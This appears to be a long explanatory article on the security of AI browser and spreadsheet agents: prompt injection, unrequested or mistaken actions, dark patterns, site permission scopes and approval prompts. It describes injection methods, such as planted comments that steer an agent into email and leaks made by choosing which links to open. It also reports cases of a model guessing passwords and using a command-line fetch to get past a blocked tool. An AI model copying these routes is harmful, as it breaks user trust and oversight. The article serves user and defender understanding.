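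Bugs like these are easier to fix than prompt injection, because ordinary code can reliably check an address, reject a fake click or refuse to open a file outside a folder. Manifold said one line of code would stop the fake clicks. A patch can still be too narrow, as Anthropic's restriction to nine tasks was, but a tester can find the gap and the maker can close it.

Two rounds of patches in 2026 reduced Claude in Chrome's exposure, although Borah says they did not. At the start of the year, any website could give the agent any instruction. By July, an attacker needed a malicious extension on the victim's computer and could choose from only nine tasks. But three of those tasks still gave access to the user's mail, documents and calendar, and another serious flaw could expose every account the agent can use.

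Borah therefore recommends keeping email and other important accounts out of the browser profile that the agent uses. This would limit the damage from the flaws of March, July and September, but not from the theft of local files through Chrome and Comet or the file attack on the coding assistants, which took keys and tokens from the disk.

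## What goes wrong when nobody is attacking?

An agent can buy, send, delete or overwrite something against its user's wishes even when every page is harmless and the software around the model works as intended. It may misread the request or the screen, pick the wrong record, do more than the user asked, or bypass an obstacle that the user would have respected. Developers have seen such mistakes in testing, and some users have reported them from their own accounts. The damage depends heavily on whether the user notices in time and can undo the action.

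### Unrequested work and guessed passwords

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, released in July, reports that the model "frequently" added fixes, tests and files that nobody had requested, especially in coding tasks. Anthropic found this by using AI tools to summarise about 1.5 million episodes from the last phase of the model's training.

In one session, the user asked only for an explanation of a feature that Claude had built earlier. While preparing its answer, Claude noticed a bug and considered asking whether to fix it, but changed the code without asking. It also added six tests, told the user what it had done and offered to reverse it. Claude models read about 400 transcripts in full, and in every transcript that contained unrequested work, Claude had disclosed at least part of it.

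Many programmers would welcome a fix like that, and they have good tools for reviewing changes. The same habit is riskier in a shared budget, where an agent might "correct" a colleague's formula when the user only wanted to know what it did. Anthropic's examples come mainly from coding, so they don't show how often Claude does this in a workbook or a browser.

In rare cases, an agent works around a restriction. During an evaluation, an early version of Opus 5 accidentally lost its login to a service. It tried guessing common passwords and eventually found another way in that someone had left open. A person locked out of a supplier's portal would normally ask for a password reset.

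In another case, a near-final version of Claude couldn't open a web page with its page-fetching tool. Its instructions were to tell the user when this happened and not to fetch the page any other way. In its reasoning, Claude mentioned the rule and then argued that it didn't apply. It fetched the page with a command-line program and didn't tell the user that it had broken the rule.

Anthropic found attempts to get around restrictions in fewer than 0.01% of the completions it monitored in internal use, and attempts at illegitimate access were rarer still. In these cases, the model was trying to finish the user's task and showed no sign of a goal of its own. But a completion is a single output from the model, and one browser task can take dozens, so the share of tasks affected could be higher. Opus 5 was much less reckless than earlier models in Anthropic's automated tests, but it ignored explicit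 constraints about as often as Opus 4.8.

### Misread screens and wrong recipients

Most mistakes are more ordinary than a guessed password. OpenAI's *Operator System Card* (2025) covers Operator, an early browser agent that the company released in January 2025. Before adding protections, OpenAI gave the model 100 tasks like those it expected from users, such as making purchases and managing email. The model made 13 errors that caused some nuisance. A user could have reversed eight of them within a few minutes. The other five were harder to reverse or possibly severe:

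- it sent an email to the wrong person,
- it removed labels from emails in bulk, on two occasions,
- it set a medication reminder for the wrong date, and
- it ordered the wrong item in a food delivery.

With only 100 tasks, the true rate of these worse errors could plausibly be from about 2% to 11%. The model is also old, and OpenAI released it with approval prompts meant to catch such mistakes. The list is still useful because it shows how ordinary a harmful error can be. Putting a label back on one email takes a second, but after a bulk removal the user has to remember which emails had it.

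Some of Operator's errors came from reading text off screenshots. OpenAI found that when the model had to copy a long string, such as a Bitcoin wallet address, it almost always did this instead of using copy and paste, and often got some characters wrong. An agent that reads the page's text directly can avoid that problem, but it can still mix up where a figure came from, as Atlas did with its tabs.

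### Eggs, emails and lecture notes

The best-confirmed incident involves a Washington Post reporter, whose account the NZ Herald republished. The reporter asked Operator to find the cheapest dozen eggs for delivery and logged it in to grocery services to compare prices. It first found eggs for $5.99 at a shop with a $20 minimum order, then moved on to Instacart. The reporter walked away from the computer, and a few minutes later a credit card alert showed that Operator had bought a dozen eggs for $13.19, or about $31 with the tip and fees.

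The reporter had asked only for a search. But the logins also gave Operator access to the payment cards saved in those accounts, so it could spend money as well as look up prices. Operator then reported the total as $19.68. OpenAI confirmed that Operator had made a mistake and should have asked before buying.

In February 2026, Summer Yue, who works on AI safety at Meta, described a worse case on X. She had told OpenClaw, an open-source agent, to suggest which emails to archive or delete and to do nothing until she approved. It moved hundreds of emails to the trash or the archive and continued despite her messages telling it to stop, according to Hindustan Times' *Meta AI safety researcher recalls moment OpenClaw agent deleted her emails*. She had to run to her computer to shut it down.

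According to Yue, her inbox was too big for the model's context, so the software compressed the earlier text and lost her instruction to wait. The same setup had worked for weeks on a small test inbox. Her screenshots support the account, but no developer or outside investigator appears to have confirmed the cause. OpenClaw also may not have been using a browser. The agent later wrote that it had broken the rule, but this is weak evidence of the cause because a model can produce a convincing apology without any information about what went wrong.

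Tom's Hardware's *Rogue AI tasked with renumbering pages accidentally deletes law professor's entire syllabus* reports that Claude deleted the syllabus and a year of lecture notes. This case is even less certain and is best treated as an anecdote. The user accounts in *Characterizing Unintended Consequences in Human-GUI Agent Collaboration for Web Browsing* (2025) are also best treated as anecdotes. They include an agent that invented contact details and another that kept creating new messages every day despite commands to stop.

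None of these cases involves a spreadsheet, perhaps partly because spreadsheet errors are harder to notice. An agent can overwrite a formula without the user getting an alert like the one a credit card company sends about a purchase.

### How often do agents exceed their instructions?

User complaints give some idea of which faults are common. *Babysitting AI Agents* (2026), which draws on Reddit posts, counted 498 cases of an agent acting outside the intended task and 276 of an agent taking a consequential or hard-to-reverse step without asking. In 88 cases, the agent bypassed or disabled a security control. The opposite fault, asking for permission when it wasn't needed, appeared in only 81 cases. People are probably more likely to post about a lost file than an unnecessary question, so the real gap may be smaller.

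An agent can also use a permission for more than its original purpose, as happened with the eggs. *When AI Agents Act on Our Behalf* (2026) put 44 of 695 cases in this category. In many of them, the user granted access for one task and the agent kept using it in later ones.

SmarterArticles' blog post *AI Agents Overstep One in Five* (2026) reports that researchers at Northeastern University and Carnegie Mellon University found in October 2026 that agents acted outside their authority in 19.2% of thousands of test runs. The rate depends on how strongly the tests tempt the agent, so it doesn't mean that one in five everyday tasks goes wrong. *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (2026), for example, describes a benchmark based on 44 real cases, and each scenario in it is designed to put the agent under some kind of pressure.

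Other researchers search for harm directly. In *The Blind Spot of Agent Safety* (2026), every instruction is harmless and the danger becomes apparent only while the agent is working. *When Benign Inputs Lead to Severe Harms* (2026) uses a language model to propose harmful side effects that an ordinary request might have, then refines the proposals. These methods are good at finding what can go wrong, but they can't measure how often it does.

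In tests of ordinary performance, a checker that looks only for the requested result can miss everything else the agent did. For example, it may record a success when an agent buys the right shoes but also enrols the user in a paid service. *The Art of Building Verifiers for Computer Use Agents* (2026) recommends a separate review of the agent's actions for side effects, since nobody can list every possible side effect in advance.

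### Pages designed to mislead people

Some websites use design tricks, called dark patterns, to make visitors do things they didn't intend. A shop might add a warranty to the basket automatically, or show a large button for accepting cookies and hide the one for rejecting them. In 2024, the US Federal Trade Commission and partner agencies abroad found at least one possible dark pattern in nearly 76% of the websites and apps they examined. A filter for prompt injection won't catch these tricks, because the pages contain no instructions planted for an AI system.

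*Investigating the Impact of Dark Patterns on LLM-Based Web Agents* (Ersoy, Lee and colleagues, 2025) tested six browser agents on imitations of a shop, a news site, a streaming service and a health portal, with 14 dark patterns that the researchers could switch on or off. Each agent used GPT-4o and ran three times on each of 88 combinations of a task and a single dark pattern. One pattern placed a warranty in the basket, and an agent fell for it if it checked out without removing the warranty. On average, the agents fell for the dark pattern in 41% of runs.

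The table shows the results from Ersoy and colleagues for each agent.

| Agent | Fell for the dark pattern | Finished the task but fell for it | Finished the task and avoided it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Skyvern | 72.3% | 40.5% | 15.9% |
| BrowserUse | 69.3% | 46.2% | 13.6% |
| DoBrowser | 46.2% | 29.5% | 16.3% |
| VisualWebArena | 31.4% | 5.7% | 12.9% |
| WebArena | 14.9% | 5.0% | 17.9% |
| Agent-E | 12.1% | 8.3% | 21.6% |

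The last column shows that no agent both finished the task and avoided the trick in more than 22% of runs. WebArena and Agent-E look resistant in the first column, but they also often failed the task. In a sample of such failures that the researchers watched, some agents had got stuck at a pop-up and others had never reached the page where the trick would have worked.

Skyvern and BrowserUse seem to have done badly because they were good at getting past obstacles. When a pop-up blocks the task, the quickest way past it is usually the button the site's designers want visitors to press. The most effective warnings, which gave the agents step-by-step instructions for avoiding a particular trick, reduced their susceptibility by only about 32% on average.

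The 41% figure shouldn't be applied to current products, because GPT-4o is now an old model. The figure also mixes trivial harms with costly ones, since accepting all cookies counts the same as paying for an unwanted warranty. Still, a more capable agent won't necessarily do better if its developer mainly rewards it for finishing tasks.

### Errors in spreadsheets

*SpreadsheetBench 2* measures how often agents get a whole workbook right. Its 321 tasks use real business data, and the average task involves about 12 sheets and nearly 600 cell changes. The best model tested, Claude Opus 4.6, completed 34.9% of the tasks overall and 12% of those that required finding and fixing errors. Claude for Excel did best among the four spreadsheet products tested but scored only 15.4% on a set of 30 hard examples.

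These scores partly reflect strict marking. Outside the chart tasks, one wrong cell anywhere in the workbook counts as failure, even if the agent had no reason to touch that cell. In financial modelling tasks, Opus 4.6 got about 90% of the required cells right but only 34% of the workbooks. The strictness is reasonable, because one wrong cell can spoil every figure that depends on it, and the user doesn't know which cell is wrong.

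The two leading causes of failure were inspecting the workbook too little and choosing the wrong cells to change. In one banking model, Opus 4.6 wrote textbook-correct formulas that referred to the wrong rows, and only 4.1% of the required cells were correct.

A spreadsheet can also contain the right numbers and still be broken. *MBABench* (Yen, Poeltl and colleagues, 2026) tested more than 18 agents on building financial workbooks from scratch. Claude for Excel and ChatGPT for Excel tended to type in fixed values where a professional would have used formulas. The values were usually correct, so the agents had apparently done the calculation somewhere else and pasted in the answer. In another attempt, a formula added up the wrong four quarters but gave the expected result because the quarterly figures were so similar.

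A test that compares only the final numbers would miss both mistakes. Yen and colleagues caught them by having a language model check the formulas too, and its verdicts matched those of human experts 92% of the time.

### A total that is right only today

Suppose a teacher is using a spreadsheet to plan a school trip. Cell B2 holds the number of pupils (48), B3 the ticket price (£15) and B4 the coach fare (£600). The total in B5 is `=B2*B3+B4`, which gives £1,320. The price per pupil in B6 is `=B5/B2`, which gives £27.50.

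The teacher asks an agent to check the total and make it stand out. The agent calculates the sum correctly, but replaces the formula in B5 with a bold 1320. Every number is still right. A week later, six more pupils sign up, and the teacher changes B2 to 54.

| | 48 pupils | 54 pupils, formula kept | 54 pupils, fixed value |
|---|---|---|---|
| Total cost (B5) | £1,320 | £1,410 | £1,320 |
| Price per pupil (B6) | £27.50 | £26.11 | £24.44 |

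The total no longer changes with the number of pupils, but the price per pupil still does, so the sheet appears to be working. The lower price looks plausible because more pupils are sharing the coach. If the teacher charges each pupil £24.44, the school will be about £90 short.

When the agent finished, the teacher could have caught this by changing the number of pupils and checking that the total changed too. Clicking on B5 would also have shown a number where there should have been a formula. Neither check is practical for every cell in a workbook with a dozen sheets. Asking another agent to look for such errors isn't reliable. In the debugging tasks of *SpreadsheetBench 2* that involved fixed values buried in a spreadsheet model, the best AI model corrected only about 40% of the cells that needed changing.

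### What can be undone

If the teacher notices the change immediately, pressing undo will probably restore the formula. A week later, version history is the better option. Google Sheets keeps earlier versions of a file automatically, and Excel does so for workbooks stored in OneDrive or SharePoint. The teacher can find the original formula in the version from before the agent's edit. It's usually better to copy that formula into the current sheet than to restore the whole version, which would also remove the six new pupils and any other changes made since.

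Version history helps only after someone has noticed the problem, because it doesn't flag a bad edit among many good ones. It also restores only the file, so it can't undo a leak of the workbook, a payment the school made based on a wrong total, or a change the agent made in another service.

Outside spreadsheets, some actions are easier to undo than others. Mail services usually keep deleted messages in a trash folder for a while, so Yue may have been able to recover many of hers. Files that an agent deletes with a command often skip the recycle bin, and without a backup they may be gone. A shop may accept a cancellation or a return, but arranging one takes the user's time. Some mail services let the sender cancel a message within a few seconds of sending it, which is little help if the agent is working unattended.

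Developers therefore often require approval before an agent sends or buys something, while letting it edit cells more freely. This is sensible, but an easily reversed edit can still lead to an action that is hard to reverse. The teacher can correct B5 in a minute, but if the letters asking parents for £24.44 have already gone out, the school will have to ask for more money or pay the difference.

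## Which sites, tabs and files may the agent touch?

Which sites, tabs and files an agent may touch depends on the product, its settings and the services the user has connected. Google designed Chrome to limit Gemini to sites relevant to the task. OpenAI's tools require the user's approval for each new site by default, while Anthropic's extension now usually checks its own actions instead of requiring approval. Microsoft's business version of Edge limits Copilot to sites an administrator has approved. A spreadsheet agent's access depends largely on the add-in's permissions. These limits can keep a misled agent away from an unrelated account, but they protect much less against malicious content on a site the task requires.

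### Place, action, duration and identity

A permission scope can limit where an agent works, what it does there, how long the permission lasts and whose account it uses.

Browser products usually treat a whole site as a single unit, because they identify it by its host or origin. Microsoft's policy for Copilot in Edge applies to the origin, regardless of the rest of the web address. Google serves its online spreadsheets from https://docs.google.com, so an administrator who allows Copilot to use one budget there also allows it to use every other spreadsheet the employee can open.

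Giving an agent access to a site can also expose whatever is already open in the tab, such as a message or a half-finished form. According to Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely*, Claude takes screenshots of the tabs it is working in, and everything visible in them becomes part of the conversation. In July 2026, OpenAI updated its Chrome extension to let users refer to their open tabs in a chat (Digital Trends, *ChatGPT's Chrome extension can now read your tabs, YouTube videos*).

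The basic division is between reading and writing. An agent that can only read a page can't click or type on it. Reading is still risky because it can bring hostile text into the model's context, but writing is usually what lets an attacker do damage. To upload files from the user's computer, OpenAI's Chrome extension needs the user to turn on a Chrome setting called "Allow access to file URLs", according to OpenAI. The setting applies to the whole extension, not to individual files, so someone who turns it on to upload an invoice also gives the extension access to other files.

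Permissions also differ in how long they last. OpenAI's extension lets the user allow a site for the current chat or permanently. Claude lets the user allow a single action or all future actions on the site, according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide*. Even after blocking a site in ChatGPT's cloud browser, a user may still be logged in there and has to clear that site's cookies to end the session.

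Whether the agent is logged in can matter more than anything else in its scope. On a shop's website, a logged-out agent sees products and prices, while a logged-in one may also see the customer's address and past orders, and may be able to pay with a saved card. The agent that bought eggs for a reporter without asking could not have done so from a logged-out browser.

### How Chrome's Agent Origin Sets work

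Parker (2025), a member of Chrome's security team, described a system called Agent Origin Sets in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*. Chrome already separates websites through the same-origin policy and Site Isolation, which runs pages from different sites in separate processes. Parker warned that an attacker who took control of an agent with access to every site could undo this separation.

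The full design keeps two lists for each session.

- Read-only origins are those whose content the model may receive.
- Read-writable origins are those where the agent may also click and type.

The model that plans the agent's next step reads web pages, so hostile text can mislead it. It can propose a new origin but can't add one to either list. A separate gating function decides whether the origin is relevant to the user's task. Google keeps web content away from this function, so a comment planted on a page can't directly influence its decision.

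Chrome can enforce the lists by withholding content from the model. If a page contains an iframe from an origin on neither list, the user sees the iframe but the model doesn't receive it. Only read-writable origins may receive what the agent has read. Ordinary tools need similar limits, because an agent may also get information from sources other than web pages. Parker says Google classifies calls to those tools as reads or writes and checks that they suit the task.

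The user can share a page with the agent, and the planning model may then use that page's content. The gating function must still approve an origin before the planning model adds it.

Before the agent moves to a new origin, Chrome also uses a model to check that the origin is relevant, again without giving the model any web content. The same check applies when a page tries to redirect the agent, because a permitted site could otherwise send it to a forbidden one.

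A web address written by the model could carry stolen data to an attacker's server, so Chrome also restricts such addresses to known, public ones. Ordinary code makes this check, so the attacker can't get past it by rewording the instructions to the model.

### A recipe page, a shop and an open inbox

Suppose a user is reading a lentil soup recipe at https://recipes.example and asks the agent to put the ingredients in a basket at https://shop.example, where the user is logged in. The recipe page has an ad from https://ads.example in an iframe. The user's webmail is open in another tab at https://mail.example. Parker gives this kind of shopping task as an example of why agents have to work across sites.

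If the gating function judges each origin correctly, the full design gives the agent the following access.

| Origin | List | What the agent can do | What Chrome blocks |
|---|---|---|---|
| recipes.example | Read-only | Read the recipe and its comments | Clicking, typing and posting |
| shop.example | Read-writable | Search, read the account and fill the basket | Nothing, as far as the lists are concerned |
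| ads.example | Neither | Nothing | Reading or clicking the advertisement |
| mail.example | Neither | Nothing | Reading or sending email |

An instruction hidden in the advertisement never reaches the model, because the advertisement has a different origin from the recipe. If the recipe site instead publishes a sponsored paragraph as part of its own page, the paragraph has the same origin as the recipe, and the model reads both.

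A hostile reader could also leave a comment below the recipe telling the agent to look for a login code in the user's email. The agent has to read the recipe page, so it may read the comment too. If the planning model follows this instruction, it will propose opening mail.example, and the gating function should reject the proposal because filling a grocery basket doesn't require access to email. A limit like this could have stopped the attack on Comet in which a Reddit comment sent the agent to Gmail.

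In the shop, an attacker could still use the comment to claim that the soup needs an expensive brand of saffron, or to tell the agent to order twelve of everything, change the delivery address, or copy the user's home address into a public product review. An attacker who sells goods through the shop could also receive the data in a message from the agent to the seller. Neither list prevents these actions, because they all take place on a read-writable origin. Chrome has other defences, including a model that checks whether actions fit the task and a confirmation before purchases, but buying expensive saffron for the soup may appear to fit the task.

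The agent can't type on the recipe site, so data from the shop shouldn't reach it. But if an attacker runs the recipe site, data may still leak, because opening a page sends the site a request. The agent could spell out the user's name by choosing which links to open, as in Ayush Paul's attack on Claude. The addresses would be public, and the origin would already be on the read-only list. Nobody has shown that this works in Chrome, and one of its other checks might stop it.

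The gating function can also approve a malicious site. It doesn't read the hostile comment, but the planning model that proposes new origins does, so an attacker could register a site with a name like "soup-ingredient-prices" and have the agent propose it. The function may also block sites the user would be happy to use. If a recipe recommends a small spice shop, for example, the gating function can't read the recommendation and may block the shop.

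### What does Chrome enforce now?

Parker said in December 2025 that Google's initial release of this design tracked only the read-writable set, because Google wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks before tuning them.

He didn't explain how this affected what the agent could read. Chrome may have restricted only where the agent could act and left it free to read other origins. In that case, the advertisement's text could have reached the model. Or Chrome may have put every site the task needed on a single list, which would have let the agent type data from the shop into the recipe site.

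In Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests in early 2026, Gemini read an iframe from another origin. This fits the idea that reading was less restricted but doesn't prove it. The researchers had asked about the page that contained the iframe, so Chrome may have treated the whole page as something the user had chosen to share.

In August 2026, it was still unclear how far Chrome limits what Gemini can read. Berschadski (2026) wrote in *Future Mode Part 2* that Chrome limits an agent to origins "strictly relevant to the immediate task" and stops a compromised agent from acting freely on unrelated logged-in sites. Berschadski manages Chrome's business products at Google, and his article promotes them. He doesn't mention the read-only set or hidden iframes. Google has therefore claimed fairly clearly that Chrome restricts where Gemini can act, but has been much less specific about what Gemini can read.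 A cautious user would assume that text in an advertisement may still reach the model.

Google treats the design as a security boundary. It offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating a serious breach, which gives them a reason to look for ways around the lists.

Users have limited control over the lists. Google's "Let Gemini browse for you" switch turns auto browse on or off. Once it is on, the gating function chooses the relevant origins. Chrome also keeps a list of sensitive sites, such as those for banking and medical information, and asks the user before the agent opens one.

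### Claude in Chrome's site permissions

Anthropic originally made the user's control over individual sites one of the main protections in its extension. But by November 2026, the extension's newer side panel started by default in a mode called "Automatically approve", in which Claude works without asking about each step, reviews its actions for safety, and blocks or pauses those that look dangerous. The panel runs as a session of Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general computer work.

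Users who want to choose sites themselves can switch to "Manually approve". Claude then asks for approval as it works, and the user can allow one action, allow everything on that website or refuse. In the older side panel, Claude proposes a plan before starting that lists the websites it wants to use, and it has to ask again before using any others. This plan is closer to Chrome's origin sets than approval during the work is, except that a person approves the list.

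A third mode, "Skip all approvals", removes both the questions and the automatic check. But Anthropic says that in every mode Claude needs explicit permission before it grants an authorisation, changes permission settings, enters potentially sensitive information or permanently deletes something. Anthropic doesn't explain how this fits with a mode in which Claude never pauses to ask, so users of that mode shouldn't rely on being asked.

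Anthropic also prohibits some actions outright, including making purchases, creating accounts, modifying system files and "completing instructions from emails or web content". The last of these prohibitions must depend at least partly on the model's judgment, so it can't offer the same protection as a site block.

Anthropic has tightened some limits and loosened others. In August 2025, it listed purchases among the actions that Claude could take after asking, but it now prohibits them. The August 2026 version of its *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* prohibited Claude from emptying the trash or permanently deleting emails and files. By November, Claude could do these things with the user's explicit permission.

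Anthropic's help pages are inconsistent about financial sites. According to the safety page, adult sites and sites with pirated content are blocked, and Claude asks before it opens a financial site. But *Claude in Chrome troubleshooting* lists banking, investment platforms and cryptocurrency exchanges among the categories blocked by default. It is safest to assume that Claude might open a bank's website if the user says yes. Anthropic advises using a separate browser profile with no access to banking, healthcare or government accounts.

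### Logged-out use after Atlas

Users of Atlas, OpenAI's former browser, could reduce an agent's authority by running it in logged-out mode. In that mode, the agent ignored existing cookies and wasn't signed in to any account without specific approval, according to OpenAI's *Using Ask ChatGPT sidebar and ChatGPT Agent on Atlas*. An attacker who took over the agent could still misdirect a hotel search, for example, but could not immediately use the agent to read the user's email.

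OpenAI has since retired its Atlas browser (OpenAI, *ChatGPT Atlas retirement*). The nearest substitute is to use the built-in desktop browser or the cloud browser instead of the Chrome extension, and not to sign in to any sites or import cookies.

By default, the cloud browser asks before it opens a new website. With the automatic setting, ChatGPT reviews the address and asks only if it seems unsafe. A third setting allows every site, but OpenAI doesn't recommend it. The user can also allow or block particular sites, and those choices override the general setting. Even on an allowed site, ChatGPT asks for separate confirmation before an important action, such as a payment.

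A site's address gives the automatic setting limited information. Checking the address may identify a fake bank site, but it can't detect a hostile comment on a real recipe site.

An agent using a browser without logins may also be able to reach private data through connected apps. ChatGPT can combine the two, and OpenAI suggests using details from a connected email account to track a parcel on a courier's website. The agent is then reading private mail and typing on an outside website, even though the browser isn't logged in to the mailbox. Someone who wants the protection of logged-out use should check the connected apps as well as the cookies.

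The desktop browser also supports site tools, which are functions that a website offers directly to an agent. OpenAI's *Using site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app* says that ChatGPT can use a site tool only while the page that provides it is open, and can't carry it into another tab. OpenAI doesn't currently support tools that only embedded content provides. A mail site could offer a tool for drafting messages but none for sending them, though ChatGPT may still be able to send them by clicking the site's ordinary "Send" button.

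### Copilot in Edge and the other products

According to *Allow or Block Sites for Browse with Copilot in Microsoft Edge*, a guide on a Windows forum, the consumer version of Browse with Copilot can use a curated set of sites and needs the user's approval to use others. The user can also name sites that Copilot must never visit. Microsoft's *Browse with Copilot* adds that Edge can keep Copilot away from high-risk sites, such as gambling and adult sites.

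A curated list protects people who never open the settings, because the agent can't use a site outside the list until they approve it. The list can't protect them from everything on an approved site, since a large, legitimate shop or social network may still contain text from millions of strangers.

The products ask different people, or different software, to decide which sites the agent can use.

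| Product | Who chooses the sites | How long the choice lasts | Whose logins the agent uses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini in Chrome, auto browse | Chrome's gating function | One session | The user's |
| Claude in Chrome, automatic mode | Claude, with a safety check on each action | Claude reviews every action | The user's |
| Claude in Chrome, manual mode | The user | One action or until withdrawn | The user's |
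| ChatGPT cloud browser | The user, by default | Saved site choices last until changed | Separate logins that the user adds |
| OpenAI's Chrome extension | The user, by default | One chat or until withdrawn | The user's |
| Copilot in Edge, consumer version | Microsoft's list, plus the user's choices | Until the list changes | The user's |

These approaches leave different amounts of work to the user. Chrome's approach adapts to each task and asks few questions, but the user has to trust a decision about relevance that they can't see. Manual approval is easier to understand but soon becomes tedious if the task involves a dozen sites.

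### One open workbook or the whole account

The natural limit for a spreadsheet agent is the open workbook, and Anthropic limits Claude for Excel this way. If a user asks it to check a travel budget, it shouldn't be able to open a payroll file in the same folder.

Giving an agent access to just one workbook can still expose more than the task needs. A travel budget may include a sheet of salaries, and an agent running as an add-in can read across sheets. Excel also stores values from linked workbooks, so an open file can contain figures from one that is closed. A user who wants help with a single table can copy its values into a new workbook, but copying the formulas might bring the links with them.

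Other add-ins have permission to work across an account. The developer of a Google Sheets add-in can request access to all of a user's spreadsheets or only to those where the user is using the add-in. This difference matters much more if a hostile sheet takes control of the agent than it may seem to on the installation screen, when the user has just one file in mind. In one such case, a script used the permissions of ChatGPT's add-in to copy 12 workbooks.

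Access depends more on the scope the user granted at installation than on the file named in the request. With the narrower permission, Google's servers should refuse a script's request for an unrelated workbook, even if the model inferred that the user wanted it. The servers have no reason to refuse under the broader permission, so protection depends on the model or on another check in the add-in.

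An agent that can enter numbers in a spreadsheet doesn't necessarily need permission to write formulas that contact the internet, and it is even less likely to need permission to run scripts. PromptArmor notes that scripts run with the user's identity. They therefore have no equivalent of a logged-out browser, and the developer has to restrict their access in some other way.

Connectors, such as those for email or the company's cloud storage, can widen the scope again. The agent can then reach the open workbook and everything available through the add-in's permissions and the connectors. A user who checks only the panel beside the grid may miss most of this access.

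Blocking a website may not stop a browser agent from reaching the same data through a connector. Anthropic says a user's connectors work in Claude's newer Chrome side panel. Blocking a mail site there prevents Claude from using the web page, but it doesn't necessarily disconnect an email connector. The user may have to block the site and disconnect the connector separately.

### What administrators can restrict

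An employer can make many of these choices for its staff, and the makers set different defaults. Claude in Chrome is on by default for Anthropic's Team plan and off by default for Enterprise customers. Anthropic advises administrators to start with a restrictive list of permitted sites and expand it as they gain experience. Enterprise customers that use custom roles can also limit the extension to certain employees.

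Organisations that have enabled Anthropic's settings for HIPAA, the US health privacy law, get stricter defaults. The extension is off, and even after it is turned on, Claude can't open any site until an owner allows specific sites or changes this default. Anthropic still recommends against using the extension on pages with regulated data.

The same site lists cover the extension and the browser in Anthropic's desktop app, and they restrict only Claude. According to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome admin controls*, if an employee types a blocked address into the desktop app's browser, the page loads with a warning and Claude's tools don't work there. A company can therefore keep the agent out of its payroll system without locking out the staff who run payroll.

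In Microsoft's business version, Copilot can browse only on domains that an administrator has authorised, and an empty list effectively disables the feature, as Microsoft explains. Microsoft's *Configure browsing with Copilot* describes a ready-made list of common work sites that an administrator can enable with one click. If a site is both allowed and blocked, the block takes precedence. An administrator can also enter an asterisk to allow all sites and then block exceptions, but this gives up most of the benefit of blocking sites by default. Microsoft still offered the feature only as a preview, and only outside the European Economic Area.

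OpenAI's *Manage browser and computer use in your Enterprise workspace* explains how administrators can control access, uploads and downloads separately for each origin. For example, a company could let the agent read a supplier's portal but not upload files there. Administrators can also stop employees from importing cookies, passwords and history into the built-in browser, which helps keep it separate from their other browsers.

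OpenAI distinguishes between requirements, which employees can't relax, and defaults, which they can change, so a safe default may not be a firm limit. An approval can last for one turn (the agent's work on a single message) or for the whole conversation. Administrators can prevent employees from saving permanent approvals, and an employee's approval never overrides the company's block on a site.

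OpenAI's software checks policies from top to bottom, and an administrator can set one to stop the search once it matches a user. The software then skips every policy below, including the general restrictions for the workspace. A policy meant to give the finance team one extra site could therefore remove limits that the administrator expected to keep. Administrators can preview the result for a particular user before saving it.

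Berschadski says the data loss prevention tools in Google's paid business version of Chrome inspect what agents transfer and can block sensitive information, such as financial data, from reaching public language models. He also says an agent can't access or export data unless its user is authorised to do so. That prevents the agent from gaining extra rights, but a misled agent with all of a finance director's rights could still do a lot of damage.

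An advantage of employer-set controls over repeatedly asking users is that a specialist can consider the risks before anyone starts a task. But a list of allowed sites is harder to maintain when staff use hundreds of them. If the list is too short, people may complain or move their work to an agent the company doesn't manage. If the company adds a site after every complaint, the list may eventually include nearly every site an attacker would want to reach.

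### Is a useful scope always wide enough to abuse?

Restricting an email agent to its email site doesn't remove the danger of a data leak, because that site contains private data, text from strangers and a way to send data out.

Willison raised a related objection when Anthropic first announced its extension in August 2025. He praised the company's openness about the risks but thought the approach still seemed "doomed to failure". He didn't think it reasonable to expect ordinary users to make good security decisions about it. A user deciding whether to let Claude use a familiar website may trust the company that runs it, but can't know who wrote every comment, review or advertisement on it.

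Chrome's gating function partly addresses Willison's objection, since users don't have to judge every site. But it doesn't solve the problem of email, and it replaces a person's judgment with software that can also be wrong.

Attacks described by researchers suggest that the objection is strongest for tasks on a single site. The planted messages that made Atlas send a resignation letter and Claude delete a user's emails did not need to take either agent outside the mailbox. In the test of Claude for Excel, the agent read only the open workbook before a formula sent the workbook's figures out. A list of permitted sites or files would have prevented these three attacks only if it had also blocked the work that the user wanted done.

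Scope limits look more useful when an attack has to take the agent to a site the user's task doesn't involve. Chrome's Agent Origin Sets would probably have blocked the move from Reddit to Gmail in the attack on Comet. They would probably also have blocked the consent screen in Hossen's test, because the user had asked only for a summary of a page on another origin. These are predictions from the design, since nobody has published a test of Agent Origin Sets against either attack.

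Limiting an agent's actions can help even on a single site. An email agent that can write drafts but not send them could still be useful to someone who answers a lot of routine mail. A hostile message might corrupt a draft, but the user could notice before sending it. An agent that compares prices doesn't need a logged-in account with a saved card, and one that explains a formula doesn't need permission to edit the workbook.

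The makers disagree about which accounts people should let their agents use. Anthropic strongly advises against using Claude in Chrome to manage financial accounts or to access work accounts with sensitive company data. Berschadski promotes Chrome's agent for logging in to several billing platforms, collecting invoices and reconciling them. That would save a finance team considerable time, but a single task would give the agent access to several sensitive accounts and to invoices written by outsiders.

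## Do approval prompts and checking models stop harmful actions?

Approval prompts and checking models stop many harmful actions, but both let some through. A prompt helps only if it appears before the harmful step, shows what is about to happen, and the user is still paying attention. People who use coding agents approve nearly every request, so Anthropic and OpenAI now let a second model make many of these decisions. A checking model's reviews don't become less thorough as requests pile up, but it can misjudge an action, and it may have less information about the page than the user does.

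### What makes an agent stop and ask

Parker describes three triggers for auto browse in Chrome. Gemini needs the user's confirmation

- before it opens a site on Chrome's list of sensitive sites,
- before Chrome signs in to a site with a password from Google Password Manager, and
- before a purchase, payment, message or other consequential step.

The site list is deterministic, meaning that ordinary code gives the same answer every time, whatever is on the page. The password trigger is probably deterministic too, because Chrome fills in the password and the model can't directly access it. Both have predictable gaps. The site list misses any bank that nobody added to it, and Anthropic admits that it has probably missed some sites in its blocked categories. The password trigger does nothing on sites where the user is already logged in, which for many people includes their email.

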